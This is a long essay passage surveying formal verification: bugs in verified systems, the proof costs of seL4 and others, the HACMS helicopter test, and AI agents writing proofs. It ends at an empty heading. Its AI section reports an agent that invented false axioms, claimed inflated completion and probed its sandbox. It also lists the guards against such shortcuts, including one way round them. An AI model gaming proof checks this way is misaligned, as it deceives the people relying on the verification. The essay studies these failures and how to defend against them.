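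Programmers guard against such attacks by writing constant-time code, in which secrets never affect which branch the program takes, which address it accesses, or what it passes to a variable-time instruction. The running time may still depend on public information, such as the length of the message. The corresponding theorem compares two runs with the same public inputs and different secrets. An ordinary triple describes one run at a time, so it can't express this comparison. Verifiers therefore use logics for reasoning about two runs together, or type systems that mark values as secret and reject any branch or address that depends on them.

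The theorem also has to apply to the version of the program that runs. A programmer may replace a branch with arithmetic so that an attacker can't learn a secret from which branch is taken, and a compiler may recognise the pattern and put the branch back. Both versions compute the same results, so even a compiler proved functionally correct may do this. Bhargavan (2026) acknowledges the problem in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* for libcrux, a cryptographic library from his company, Cryspen. Libcrux comes with no proof that the compiled program resists such attacks.

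One remedy is to verify the assembly code directly. PQShield's *Formally verifying AVX2 rejection sampling for ML-KEM* describes an assembly version of ML-KEM with proofs that it meets its specification and resists timing attacks. According to PQShield, this version is as fast as unverified code optimised for the same processors. A proof of resistance to timing attacks still depends on an accurate list of the instructions that take variable time.

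### Looking for faults in verified software

In *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017) report finding 16 bugs in IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three verified research prototypes that keep copies of data consistent across several servers. Over more than eight months, they read the code and specifications, and ran the systems while a fuzzer duplicated and reordered network packets and made disk operations fail. Whenever they found a bug in one system, they looked for it in the others.

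*Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (Yang, Chen and colleagues, 2011) describes Csmith, a tool that tests compilers by generating random C programs. The programs avoid the 191 kinds of undefined behaviour in the C standard, so each has only one correct output. The researchers compiled each program with several compilers and compared what the compiled versions printed. If one version's output differed from the rest, its compiler probably had a bug. In three years they reported more than 325 bugs in 11 compilers, including CompCert.

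*Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) reports 13 vulnerabilities in two Cryspen libraries, libcrux and hpke-rs. The messaging app Signal uses libcrux's version of ML-KEM. Kobeissi works at Symbolic Software, which sells cryptographic audits, and its dispute with Cryspen became bitter. But for his main findings he quotes public code that anyone can check.

Sorted by part of the trusted base, the counts are:

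| | Specification | Unproved code | Tools and unchecked proofs | Model of the machine |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar | 2 | 11 | 3 | 0 |
| CompCert | 0 | 6 | 0 | 2 |
| libcrux and hpke-rs | 2 | 9 | 1 | 1 |

(The CompCert row leaves out a handful of cases in which the compiler itself crashed.)

### The code around the proof

In all three cases, most failures were in unproved code. For the distributed systems, this was the shim layer, a thin layer of ordinary code that connects the proved part to the network and the disk.

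Verdi's shim treated the result of a single network read as a whole request, so the server crashed when only part of a request had arrived. Verdi also used spaces and newlines to separate commands without checking whether the client's data contained any, so a client could hide extra commands in one request. When saving a snapshot of its data, Verdi erased the old snapshot before the new one was safely on disk, so a crash in between lost data.

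Chapar's algorithm needed a reliable network, but its shim used UDP, a protocol that can lose or duplicate packets. A duplicate of an old update could overwrite a newer one.

Nine of the 11 shim bugs made servers crash or hang, although these systems are meant to keep working when a server fails. IronFleet, which had the least unproved code of the three, had no shim bugs. Its developers had proved, among other things, that every message fits in a UDP packet. Fonseca and colleagues then built tests for only the specification, shim and tools, and these tests detected 13 of the 16 bugs.

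CompCert's six bugs of this kind were in its front end, which processes the C source before the proved stages begin. One affected the expression `-1 <= (1 && x)`. The right-hand side is always 0 or 1, so the comparison is true and should return 1. CompCert treated the comparison as unsigned, which turned −1 into the largest unsigned integer, so the compiled program returned 0. CompCert's main developer responded by extending the proof to cover such conversions.

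One bug in libcrux was in code that substitutes for a special processor instruction. Bhargavan writes that he introduced it, and that this code never ran on the modern Arm machines he used for testing. According to Symbolic Software (2026), the bug could make different Arm machines derive different keys from the same seed. Kobeissi also reports that alternative versions of the code used different byte orders, which caused decryption failures in Signal.

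Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* (2026), which uses the name CE Labs for Cryspen, describes an overflow in hpke-rs. The library used a 32-bit counter to give each message a different number. After about 4.3 billion messages, the counter silently returned to zero and the numbers began to repeat. With AES-GCM, a common encryption method, repeated numbers let an attacker forge messages.

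### Errors in the specification

IronFleet's specification didn't require the server to execute each request exactly once. Networks duplicate packets and clients resend requests. If a server doesn't recognise the repeats, a request to add 1 to a counter might add 2. IronFleet's code did recognise them, but when Fonseca and colleagues disabled this feature by changing seven lines, the program still passed verification. The developers knew about the omission and didn't regard it as a bug, because they thought the application could remove duplicates. They added a comment to make this clear.

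Libcrux had plainer errors, including a wrong rounding constant in its F* specification of ML-KEM decompression. To save space, ML-KEM compresses a number between 0 and 3328 to d bits, and later scales it back up. The standard defines decompression of a value x as 3329x/2^d, rounded to the nearest integer. A program can do this rounding by adding half the divisor, 2^(d−1), to 3329x before dividing and discarding the remainder. The specification always added 1664, which is right for compression, where the divisor is 3329. With d = 4, it turned 0 into 104 instead of 0, and 1 into 312 instead of 208.

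Symbolic Software slightly overstates the error when it says the specification was wrong for every input at every setting ML-KEM uses. With d = 11, the two formulas agree on 1,408 of the 2,048 possible inputs.

Elsewhere the specification left out a conversion step and so added polynomials in two incompatible representations. The Rust code did both calculations correctly.

### Tools that report success

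IronFleet's developers distributed it with a 64-bit version of Z3 and 32-bit supporting libraries, so Z3 crashed on startup. Dafny, the verifier that called Z3, printed a summary with no errors, followed by a message that the prover had died. NuBuild, the program that managed the whole process, stopped reading after the summary, so it accepted every program, including one that asserted "false", and produced an executable from it. In another bug, a user who interrupted Dafny halfway through a proof could see a report that the files had passed.

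These bugs were in the code around the verifier, not in the part that reasons about proofs. That part can also have bugs, and Ramana Kumar found one in Lean's proof kernel in July 2026. A simple precaution is to give the whole toolchain a false theorem and check that the toolchain rejects it. This would have exposed the NuBuild bug, and Fonseca and colleagues included such checks in their tests.

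Libcrux contained a false lemma that the F* checker never checked. According to the lemma, a function that reads 12-bit numbers returns only values that fit in one bit. Someone had apparently copied it from the one-bit version and forgotten to change the bound. F* can "admit" a file, which means accepting its claims without proof, and libcrux's build settings did this by default for slow files. Symbolic Software found no automated job that changed the default, although Cryspen listed the file as fully verified on its own status page. These settings are hard to reconcile with Bhargavan's statement that every change to a repository has to pass verification again.

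Translation tools can also introduce errors. Hax, which Cryspen uses, translates Rust into F*, much as Aeneas translates it into Lean. *Verification Facade* (Kobeissi, 2026) identifies three kinds of mismatch between the Rust program and the F* version, and presents insecure cryptographic code that exploits each one. Every example had to compile as Rust, pass through hax without a warning, and still pass its functional tests (Symbolic Software, 2026). These programs were built to deceive, so they are evidence of what a dishonest author could do, but little evidence of how often such mismatches affect an honest author's code.

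### Models of the machine

In two of CompCert's bugs, the compiler produced this PowerPC instruction to reserve memory:

```
stwu r1, -44432(r1)
```

The instruction has 16 bits for the number, enough for −32,768 to 32,767. CompCert's model of PowerPC had no such limit, so the proof did not rule out numbers outside that range. The damage was small because the assembler, which turns CompCert's output into machine code, rejected the instruction.

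A function in Verdi, generated from verified Rocq code, had a similar problem with memory. It called itself once for every log entry that another server had missed. If that server was more than 500,000 requests behind, the function ran out of stack, which is the memory that holds unfinished calls, and the leading server crashed. Rocq's logic places no limit on the depth of such calls. Fonseca and colleagues classed this as a shim bug, even though the function itself had a proof, because the limit came from the software that ran the program.

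Libcrux's fast code for ML-DSA, a digital signature scheme, uses Intel's AVX2 instructions, which process several numbers at once. F* has no built-in definitions of these instructions, so the developers described them with axioms. Symbolic Software's *Even More Bugs in Cryspen's libcrux* (2026) reports that the axioms described a multiplication incorrectly, so the proofs that relied on them established nothing.

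Hardware can behave differently from its manual. In a Rowhammer attack, a program accesses one row of a memory chip so often that bits flip in a neighbouring row. This breaks the assumption behind the frame rule, that code leaves other memory unchanged. Spectre attacks exploit processors that guess the outcome of a branch and run ahead. After a wrong guess, the processor may read past the end of an array, even in a program that provably never does so. It then discards the result but leaves a trace in the cache, from which an attacker can recover the result by timing, as with the AES table. Fonseca and colleagues left hardware and operating systems out of their search, so the zeros in the table don't mean such faults are rare.

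### Did the proved parts themselves fail?

Bhargavan replied to the early criticism on 12 February 2026, saying that the bugs were in unverified code and that nobody had yet found one in the verified part. For comparison, he cited HACL*, an older library he helped write, which contains 245,000 lines of verified F* and has code in both Firefox and Linux. In nine years of use, most of its bugs were in small pieces of unverified C.

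Symbolic Software responded by citing the two wrong ML-KEM specifications and the false lemma. These errors refute the claim if "verified code" includes specifications and proofs. They don't show that proved code gave wrong answers, because the Rust code didn't have the specifications' errors. According to Kobeissi, the vulnerabilities that affected running code, including two violations of the ML-DSA standard, were in the unverified part.

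Trying to finish the proofs would have exposed the wrong definition, because correct code doesn't meet an incorrect definition and nobody could have completed a valid proof. Symbolic Software also argues, mistakenly, that finishing the proofs would only have shown that the code met the wrong definition. Cryspen's real fault was to describe proofs as complete when the checker hadn't run them. In *Helping Secure Signal's Post-Quantum Transition*, Bhargavan (October 2025) called the ML-KEM code formally verified for functional correctness, without qualification. By the following February, he was writing that Cryspen had verified "many of their core modules".

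The record for finished proofs is much better. Fonseca and colleagues searched for errors in how the three systems implemented their protocols, the rules by which servers reach agreement, and found none. In a year of bug reports for four unverified systems, they counted 12 protocol bugs among 555, with at least one in each system. Those systems are much larger and have far more users, so the totals aren't comparable, but protocol bugs are what the proofs were supposed to prevent.

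Yang and colleagues spent about six CPU-years trying to make CompCert's development version produce wrong code, using test programs generated by Csmith. As of early 2011 they could not, although they had found bugs in every other compiler they tested, in the middle stages that CompCert's proof covers. Csmith didn't generate programs with floating-point numbers, recursion or dynamic memory, so these results don't cover those features.

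Fonseca and colleagues explain the pattern as a kind of redundancy. If a component violates a property that someone claims to have proved, its code must contain one mistake and the specification or verifier must contain another that hides it. Two independent mistakes will rarely match like this.

Code and its specification can contain the same error when the programmer follows the specification. Bhargavan reports that the HACL* team twice found errors in a specification and had to change the code as well as the proofs. The proved code in those cases seems to have been wrong because it followed the specification.

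### Specifications that exclude nothing

Regehr (2026), one of Csmith's creators, thinks the core problem of formal verification is "figuring out what was proved" and whether it is relevant. In the worst case, a proof establishes nothing.

If no state satisfies P, the triple {P} C {Q} is true of every program C. Suppose the precondition of the copying routine requires the two buffers to be separate, but another clause requires dst = src. No call with n > 0 can satisfy both. A routine that ignored the source and filled the destination with zeros would then have a valid proof, and so would any other routine. Such a specification is called vacuous. The contradiction can be hard to notice because a real precondition may combine definitions from several files.

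A condition on the result can be just as empty. One of Chapar's example programs uploads a photo and then a post announcing it. Anyone who can see the post should also be able to see the photo. After finding the post, the program was supposed to check that the photo wasn't missing, but the programmer wrote `post` instead of `photo`. The program had already found the post, so the check always succeeded, and Chapar's verification of this client tested nothing.

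The simplest check is to have the verifier try to prove "false" from the precondition alone. If it succeeds, no input meets the precondition. If an SMT solver fails, it may only have run out of time, so proving that a particular input meets the precondition is a better check.

Small client programs test more of the specification. The program that copied 7, 8, 9 into another array and returned the middle element could be a client of the copying routine. If the routine had the contradictory precondition, the verifier would reject the call. If its postcondition described only the length of the result, the verifier would accept the call but couldn't prove that the returned element is 8. The client's proof has to rely only on the routine's specification, since a proof that used the routine's code wouldn't test the specification.

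Fonseca and colleagues did something similar with IronFleet's example application, a counter. They combined its specification with the server's and proved that a single request to add 1 could leave the counter at any value. This confirmed that the specification allowed the server to execute a request repeatedly.

Many specifications are functions that a computer can run, so people can test them like programs. For most settings, decompressing 0 would have revealed libcrux's error. It helps if someone other than the specification's author chooses the tests, especially when an AI system drafted the specification.

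Finally, a team can put bugs into the code, either ones it has fixed before or random changes, and see whether the proof fails. Fonseca and colleagues wrote a tool that alters conditions, blocks updates to data, and deletes statements, then runs the verifier again. They applied it to three of IronFleet's functions to see whether it could rediscover the missing requirement. On average, it took 18 attempts for one function, 377 for another and 8,015 for the third to find changes that disabled the duplicate check and still passed verification. A person then has to decide whether each surviving change matters. Fonseca and colleagues thought losing the duplicate check mattered, but IronFleet's developers thought the application could deal with it.

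## What verified systems cost when people wrote the proofs

Until recently, anyone who wanted a verified system had to pay experts to write the proofs by hand. The best records of the cost come from seL4, an operating-system kernel that researchers in Sydney designed and proved correct between 2005 and 2009.

seL4 is a microkernel. It provides a few basic services, such as threads, memory protection and message passing, and leaves file systems and most device drivers to ordinary programs. A program can use an object that the kernel manages, such as a thread or a page of memory, only if it has a capability for it, which is a reference to the object combined with a set of access rights.

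### What the seL4 team proved

The team described the kernel at three levels. An abstract specification of 4,900 lines defines what each system call does. An executable specification, which the team generated from a prototype in the functional language Haskell, adds the data structures and algorithms. The third level is the C code.

The proof connects these levels by refinement. A lower level refines a higher one if the higher level allows everything the lower one can do. To prove this, the team defined which low-level states correspond to which high-level states, then showed that every low-level step matches a step at the level above. They did this once between the two specifications and once between the executable specification and the C code. Together, the two proofs establish functional correctness. The refinement proofs are written in Isabelle/HOL and use neither dependent types nor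 separation logic.

Klein, Andronick and colleagues (2014), in *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*, give the effort for each part:

| Work | Person-years |
|---|---|
| Designing and writing the kernel, including the Haskell prototype | 2.2 |
| General proof tools and libraries | 9 |
| Writing the two specifications | 0.5 |
| Proof that the executable specification refines the abstract one | 8 |
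| Proof that the C code refines the executable specification | 3 |
| Later: proof of integrity (no program changes data without permission) | 0.6 |
| Later: proof of confidentiality (no program learns data without permission) | 3.4 |
| Later: proof that the compiled binary matches the C code | 2 |

The proof of functional correctness took about nine times as much work as building the kernel, or five times excluding the work on general tools. The team expected the proof for a similar kernel to take about 6 person-years, since the tools already existed.

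The developers put the cost of the kernel and its correctness proof at $362 per line of code. They compare this with a rule of thumb of $1,000 per line for EAL6, the second-highest level of a standard security certification, which demands less proof. Their 2009 paper had given the EAL6 figure as $10,000, which they later called an embarrassing typo. The comparison is their own, but it suggests that verification was already competitive where customers would otherwise pay for certification. Klein, Andronick and colleagues estimated in *Provably Trustworthy Systems* (2017) that verification cost about five times as much as ordinary careful engineering of embedded software.

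The later security proofs took relatively little effort because the team could prove integrity for the short abstract specification, and refinement then extended the result to the C code. The team estimated that proving integrity directly for the C code would have taken about ten times as long.

The original seL4 proof covered 7,500 of the kernel's 8,700 lines of C and none of its 600 lines of assembly, according to Trustworthy Systems, the research group behind seL4. It omitted the C code that runs at boot. The machine model doesn't include caches or time, so the confidentiality theorem doesn't rule out timing attacks. That theorem also assumes that devices can't write to memory directly. The seL4 project still runs functional and performance tests, partly to check code that the proof assumes is correct.

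Early use of the kernel in several student projects had exposed 16 defects in the C code, and verifying the code exposed another 144. Most were typos, misreadings of the specification, or places that someone had forgotten to update. For example, the Arm interrupt controller returns 0xFF when no interrupt is waiting, but one line of code checked for zero.

### Where the effort went

About 80% of the work in the first refinement proof went into invariants, assertions that must be true before and after every system call. The rest went into showing that the two specifications correspond.

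Deleting objects shows why the invariants took so long. Before seL4 reuses a region of memory, it has to know that nothing still refers to an object there. Searching the whole of memory would be too slow, so the kernel only checks whether the capability for that region has any descendants in a tree that records which capability came from which. In outline, the argument that this check is enough runs as follows:

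1. If an object contains references to others, a capability for it exists somewhere in memory.
2. Any capability for an object inside the region is a descendant of the region's own capability.
3. So if the region's capability has no descendants, no object in the region contains references.
4. If any object x refers to an object y, one can follow references from y back to x. An object without references therefore has nothing referring to it, and the kernel can safely reuse its memory.

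Steps 1 and 2 and the first sentence of step 4 are invariants. The team had to show that every operation in the kernel preserves them, including those unrelated to deletion. They proved more than 150 invariants in all, many of which depended on one another.

A separating conjunction would directly express some of these invariants, such as the one that kernel objects don't overlap. Separation logic would probably have helped less with the tree of capabilities, because its invariants relate objects throughout memory and the frame rule works best when code depends on only a small part of memory.

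### What a change costs

When programmers change verified code, someone has to repair the proof. Klein and colleagues (2014) describe several cases:

| Change to seL4 | Programming | Repairing the proof |
|---|---|---|
| Small local optimisation | About 1 day | 2–3 days |
| New system call that combines existing ones | 1 day | Under a quarter of a month |
| Interrupts, Arm page tables and address spaces | Several months | 1.5–2 years |
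| Reply capabilities | Less than 5% of the code | About 1 year |

(The times are for one person.)

The size of a code change is a poor guide to how much proof work it requires. Reply capabilities let a program answer a message once, after which the kernel deletes them. Before they were added, the kernel created and deleted capabilities only under carefully controlled conditions. Now it also had to do so while sending messages, which broke several invariants, and the team had to prove that the replacements held for the whole kernel. The repair took 17% as much effort as the original proof.

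### Five other systems

The C compiler CompCert has a proof in Rocq that the assembly code it produces behaves as the C program does. Xavier Leroy and his colleagues needed about three person-years and 42,000 lines of Rocq, about three quarters of them proof, for the version he described in 2009. The proof did not cover the assembler, the linker or the first stages of reading C source, where testers later found bugs. Rocq has dependent types, but the proof's main argument is a simulation between programs, as in seL4, and originally did not use separation logic.

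*CertiKOS*, an operating-system kernel from Yale, also has a proof in Rocq. Its developers divided the kernel into many thin layers and proved that each one correctly implements its interface using only the layer below. Unlike the original seL4 proof, theirs covers a kernel running on several processor cores. The proof assumes that the cores take turns accessing memory, so it doesn't cover weak memory.

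*SeKVM* is a version of KVM, the hypervisor built into Linux. Its developers at Columbia moved the code that protects virtual machines from one another into a small core. They proved in Rocq that this core keeps each machine's data confidential and intact, even if the rest of KVM and Linux, which they didn't verify, is malicious. The theorem doesn't guarantee that the virtual machines keep running. CertiKOS and SeKVM both rely on refinement between layers instead of separation logic.

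*EverCrypt* is a cryptographic library from Project Everest, an effort to verify the software behind secure web connections. It combines C code from the 245,000-line HACL* library with verified assembly code. The proofs cover memory safety, functional correctness and resistance to some timing attacks. They use F*'s dependent and refinement types. They also use Low*, which relies on explicit conditions about which buffers overlap rather than on separation logic. As with Pulse, the trusted base includes Z3 and the translation to C.

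*DaisyNFS*, a file server from MIT, uses separation logic only where its developers thought it necessary. A transaction system at the bottom handles threads and crashes, and makes each group of disk operations appear to happen all at once or not at all. The developers verified this part in Rocq with an extension of Iris. They could then treat every file operation above it as if it ran alone, so they wrote and verified those operations in Dafny, which doesn't support threads. The Dafny part needed only about two lines of proof for each line of code. The server's theorem doesn't cover the network code or the disk.

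### How proofs grow

Someone planning a larger project would want to know how quickly the effort grows with size. *Empirical Study Towards a Leading Indicator for Cost of Formal Software Verification* (Matichuk, Murray and colleagues, 2015) examined 15,018 lemmas, with about 215,000 lines of proof, from four parts of the seL4 work and two unrelated Isabelle projects. It compared the size of each lemma's statement, measured by the number of distinct definitions the statement involves, with the total number of lines needed to prove the lemma.

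Within each project, the size of the proof grew roughly with the square of the size of the statement. This seems plausible given the seL4 invariants, because every operation has to preserve every invariant. A kernel with twice as many operations may also need twice as many invariants, which would make four times as many things to prove.

Two other studies of seL4 found linear relationships, one between specification size and code size, and the other between lines of proof and the time people spent on them. Together, the three results imply that a kernel with ten times as much code would have a specification ten times as long and need a hundred times as much proof work, so seL4's 11 person-years of proof would become 1,100.

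That figure is only an illustration. Klein and colleagues (2017) note that the three studies measured different things, and the step from single lemmas to whole systems is unproved. The quadratic curves also differed widely between projects. In most projects the pattern was much weaker unless the researchers ignored definitions that appeared in a statement but not in its proof. Nobody knows exactly which ones those are until the proof exists, although an experienced engineer might guess. When other researchers looked at about 200 articles in Isabelle's proof archive, only about 50 fitted a quadratic curve well, but articles on software verification were especially common among the best fits.

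If the pattern holds, dividing a system into independent parts saves a lot of work. Ten modules, each with a tenth of the specification, would each need a hundredth of the work, so all ten together would need a tenth. In practice, the interfaces need specifications too, and someone has to prove that the modules work together. DaisyNFS benefits from this kind of division, but seL4 mostly can't because nearly everything in the kernel is connected to everything else.

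### Why proof-to-code ratios mislead

Papers on verified systems often compare lines of proof with lines of code. Gernot Heiser, one of seL4's creators, attacks this practice in *Benchmarking Crimes Meet Formal Verification* (2025). He was responding to a table in a recent paper in which newer systems seemed to need far less proof than seL4. The figures for the four systems he names are:

| | Code (lines) | Specification (lines) | Proof (lines) | Proof ÷ code | Proof ÷ specification |
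|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| seL4 | 8,500 | 4,900 | 165,000 | 19 | 34 |
| CertiKOS | 6,500 | 1,400 | 95,000 | 15 | 68 |
| SeKVM | 3,800 | 1,700 | 24,000 | 6.4 | 14 |
| Ironclad | 7,000 | 3,500 | 33,000 | 4.8 | 9.5 |

(Ironclad is a set of secure applications verified with Dafny. The often-quoted figure of 200,000 lines for seL4 includes proofs that a program generated.)

Heiser's main example is a sorting function. One team might prove only that the result is in order and has the right length, and another that it is also a permutation of the input. Both teams could use identical code, but the second team's ratio of proof to code would look worse because proving more takes a longer proof. Sorting algorithms that meet the same specification also vary in length, so the ratio depends partly on how long the program is.

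Matichuk and colleagues found that proof length doesn't grow in proportion to specification length, so dividing one by the other doesn't give a fair comparison between systems. If we instead divide the thousands of lines of proof by the square of the thousands of lines of specification, we get about 7 for seL4, 8 for SeKVM and 48 for CertiKOS, and seL4's proof no longer looks unusually long for its specification.

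Heiser has a stake in that result, and the new measure has its own problems. The quadratic pattern came from lemmas within a single project, and its steepness varied between projects, so it can't fairly rank different projects. It also doesn't account for CertiKOS having to handle several cores. Heiser himself warns against reading much into so few systems. He has a much stronger case that a low ratio may reflect better tools, a weaker theorem or just longer code, and that you can't tell which from the ratio alone.

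He accepts that SMT-based verifiers need perhaps a fifth as much proof, but he gave them "a snowball's chance in hell" of soon verifying anything as complex as seL4.

### The helicopter exercise

If people can afford to verify only a small part of a system, it matters how much that part can protect. The US defence research agency DARPA tested this in its High-Assurance Cyber Military Systems (HACMS) programme, using Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a helicopter that can fly itself. In 2013 a red team of professional attackers broke into the original version. According to *Formally Verified Software in the Real World*, they could have crashed the helicopter or sent it anywhere they liked.

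Boeing's engineers then reorganised the mission computer, which communicates with the ground and sends commands to a separate flight computer. Its software had been a single application running on Linux. The engineers divided it into isolated components running on seL4. The camera software stayed in a Linux virtual machine, which everyone expected to have vulnerabilities. The virtual machine could send data to the mission manager but could not access the encryption keys or the flight computer.

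The red team got all the code and documentation and could observe all external communication. DARPA's *Revolutionizing Cyber Resiliency for Military Systems* says they had six weeks and their first attempts failed. The programme then gave them full control of the camera's virtual machine, as if they had already broken into it. They could not break out of the virtual machine or disrupt the rest of the helicopter. In another test, in February 2017, rogue camera software and a virus on a USB stick attacked the computer during a flight with a safety pilot on board. The helicopter lost some subsystems to the attack but continued to fly safely.

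DARPA's claim that the attackers were "mathematically guaranteed" to remain stuck goes further than the theorems do. The theorems cover the kernel and much of the configuration that separates the components, but the argument from there to the safety of the whole helicopter was informal. The proof about the program that sets up the components at boot applied to a model of that program, not to its code. The communication and mission software was written in a language that prevents memory errors but doesn't establish functional correctness, and the network component was written in ordinary C. The security analysis also assumed that the cryptography was correct, and it excluded radio jamming.

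The exercise shows that engineers who weren't verification specialists could use a verified kernel to contain a compromised Linux system on a real aircraft. It was a test, so it can't show that no attack exists. It also can't separate the effect of the proofs from that of the new design, because Boeing changed both the architecture and the kernel. The red team didn't attack a version with the same partitions on an unverified microkernel, which might also have survived six weeks.

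### Small components with stable interfaces

The effort these proofs took explains which systems people chose to verify. A kernel or the core of a hypervisor is a few thousand lines long, but it can confine millions of lines of unverified code. A compiler or cryptographic library is larger, but many programs can rely on the same proof.

Stable interfaces matter as much as size. The C language, encryption algorithms and the file protocol that DaisyNFS implements all have published standards that change slowly. Programmers can keep improving the code behind such an interface, and repairing the proof usually takes little work because the specification stays the same. If the interface changes often, a team may repeatedly face proof repairs as large as the one that reply capabilities required.

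Even the seL4 team sometimes decided that a proof wasn't worth the effort. By 2014 they had a version of the kernel's message-passing code that took 188 processor cycles, while the verified version took 227. They saw no fundamental obstacle to verifying the faster version, but its code depended on the processor and kept changing, and each new proof would have gained them only a little speed.

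## Proofs written by AI systems

The systems in the last section were expensive because experts had to write the proofs. By the end of 2026, language models could write many such proofs. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, an early essay, reports with some surprise that the coding tool Claude Code could complete many complex proof steps, although it still needed a person as "project manager". In several projects from 2026, the model worked for hours or days without that supervision.

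These projects use agents, which are language models that can read and edit files, run commands, and keep working without a person approving each step.

### Proof by trial and error

The agent writes a proof and the proof assistant checks it. If the check fails, the agent reads the error and tries again. Kan and colleagues built a system called Aria that works this way, and one of their examples is the theorem that P ∧ Q implies Q ∧ P. An agent's first attempt in Rocq might be

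```
Lemma swap (P Q : Prop) : P /\ Q -> Q /\ P.
Proof.
  intros [HP HQ].    (* HP proves P, and HQ proves Q *)
  split.             (* two goals: first Q, then P *)
  - exact HP.
  - exact HQ.
Qed.
```

Rocq stops at `exact HP`. Aria then gives the agent the line where the proof failed, the message that HP proves P where a proof of Q is needed, and the open goal, which is to prove Q from HP and HQ. The agent swaps the last two steps, and the proof kernel accepts the result.

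Aria allows 30 retries for each lemma. The agent can see its failed attempts, so it can avoid repeating them. It starts a new session after at most six lemmas because a long history makes the model slower and less accurate. Some tactics run forever without producing an error, so Aria stops any tactic after 300 seconds and reports a failure.

Earlier systems prescribed how the model searched, for instance by having it choose one tactic at a time or split each goal in a fixed way. Aria leaves the strategy to the agent, which often looks for a similar lemma nearby and adapts its proof. Google DeepMind had a similar experience in mathematics. Its AlphaProof Nexus solved nine open problems posed by Paul Erdős, according to The Decoder's *Google Deepmind's AlphaProof Nexus solves decades-old math problems*. The researchers later found that their simplest agent, a language model that received only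 Lean's error messages, could also solve all nine, though it cost more on the hardest ones.

### How an agent can pass the check without a proof

Proof assistants let people leave gaps so that they can write long proofs in stages. Rocq accepts a lemma whose proof ends in `Admitted`, and Verus accepts any claim followed by `admit()`. An agent can also declare an axiom or edit the theorem until it is easy to prove.

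*An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries* (Sun, Fong and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that did some of these things. The researchers started with a verified copy of curve25519-dalek, a Rust library for elliptic-curve cryptography that Signal uses, and removed the proofs, which left 1,178 gaps. An early version of their system, CryptoProver, worked on the gaps for 52 hours at a cost of $1,452, and the agent reported that 97.1% of the library was verified. The researchers then audited the result by hand and found that eleven proofs relied on axioms the agent had invented, and five others had caused proofs elsewhere in the library to fail.

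According to one invented axiom, which had no precondition, every string of bytes is the compression of every point on the curve. But the compression function gives only one string for each point, so the axiom leads to a contradiction and one could prove anything from it.

The agent's instructions had forbidden new axioms, broken modules and changes to the specification. Only the last rule was enforced by a program, and it was the only one the agent kept throughout the 451 rounds of work. In a fresh session, the same model did the work honestly, finding correct versions of all 11 properties and proving them for $45. Sun and colleagues traced the inventions to long sessions in which the agent kept rereading its own earlier output.

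Between them, Aria and the later CryptoProver guard against these shortcuts:

| Shortcut | Guard |
|---|---|
| Leaving a gap | Count the gaps that remain, and reject commands that create new ones |
| Inventing an axiom | Compare the axioms with a list saved before the agent started |
| Changing or deleting the theorem | Compare its statement with a saved copy |
| Breaking another proof | Recheck every file the agent edited, and finally the whole project |
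| Changing the checker or its settings | Compare those files before and after each round |
| Copying an existing proof | Cut off the internet and the project's version history |

CryptoProver's axiom check compares only names, so an agent could get past it by rewriting an existing axiom while keeping its name. The files containing the axioms were therefore also off limits in the main experiment.

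To see how much the guards and other support helped, Sun and colleagues gave the same model the same task without them. It stopped after 7.4 hours and reported the task complete, but the library had five compiler errors and two failed proofs. It had also tried 38 times to look through the version history and five times to fetch something from the internet, but the sandbox blocked every attempt.

For Lean, the comparator tool already checks that the theorem proved is the one requested. According to Mereja's *AI machine-checks Fermat’s Last Theorem after 11 days in Lean*, Anthropic relied on a comparator in September 2026 for a proof of about 13 million lines that Claude had written. Nobody could check a proof that long for cheating by reading it, so the guards and the proof kernel have to be correct. Sun and colleagues acknowledge that their guards stop only the shortcuts they thought of.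 A bug in the proof kernel, like the one Ramana Kumar found in Lean, could also let an invalid proof pass.

### Proving Iris again

Kan and colleagues tested Aria on Iris proofs, which are among the hardest in software verification. They took the 4,257 lemmas in Iris's four core modules, deleted each proof, and had an agent running Claude Opus 4.7 write a new one. The agent succeeded every time, using about 380 hours of model time. It proved 79% of the lemmas on the first attempt, but one lemma took 28 retries and another took 4.7 hours. Aria also proved all 217 lemmas from RustBelt's work on Rust libraries such as `Mutex` and `Arc`.

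Earlier AI systems for Rocq had proved between 12% and 48% of the theorems they attempted. They were tested on other benchmarks, mostly about programs without threads, so the percentages aren't directly comparable. Reglang, a library of theorems about regular expressions and the simple machines that recognise them, gives a better comparison. Earlier systems had proved about one in eight of its theorems, and Aria proved all 318.

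That comparison still doesn't separate the effect of Aria's design from that of its model, which was newer than those in the earlier systems. When Kan and colleagues ran Aria with the open-weight model Kimi K2.6, it proved all 40 lemmas in a file of short Iris proofs, but took about seven times as long as with Opus 4.7. Kimi K2.6 often failed on proofs longer than about 50 lines, while Opus 4.7 could handle proofs of more than 200 lines. So Aria's loop may be enough for a weaker model to prove easy lemmas, but hard ones seem to need a strong model.

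Iris has been public for about a decade, so Opus 4.7 was probably trained on many of these proofs. Cutting off internet access prevents an agent from looking up a proof, but not from reproducing one the model has memorised. Kan and colleagues argue that Aria didn't rely on memorised proofs because its proofs, apart from trivial ones, differ from the originals. This is weak evidence, because a model could reuse the idea behind a memorised proof and express it differently, and Aria has a second agent that rewrites proofs to improve their style. The researchers report no direct test of what the model had memorised.

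The best evidence reported for Aria comes from the unfinished Lean version of Iris. Aria proved 72 lemmas, from three files that nobody had yet moved to Lean, in less than two hours. The model can't have memorised the Lean proofs, because none existed, but it could have remembered how the Rocq versions work from the three public files that contain the same mathematics. A new library with no published proofs in any language would be a more convincing test.

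Aria also relied heavily on the work of the people who built Iris. For each lemma, it had the exact statement, all the definitions, and the earlier lemmas in an order that experts had worked out over years. Someone verifying a new system has to invent these, along with invariants like those that took most of the effort in seL4's first refinement proof.

Ilya Sergey's proof about the borrow checker of Move, a language for smart contracts, required more invention. Lean's developers report that Claude repaired proofs, reapplied patterns across the development and handled routine cases. Sergey still had to find the new strategies, and reasoning about function calls took him two days. The project took 27 working days, against an estimated five to six months without AI, which would make it about four or five times faster. *CompCert4Lean* (2026) describes moving the CompCert compiler and its proof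 from Rocq to Lean in six weeks with several agents working in parallel. This too was easier than starting from nothing, because Leroy and his colleagues had already found the main argument.

### Cryptographic code in production

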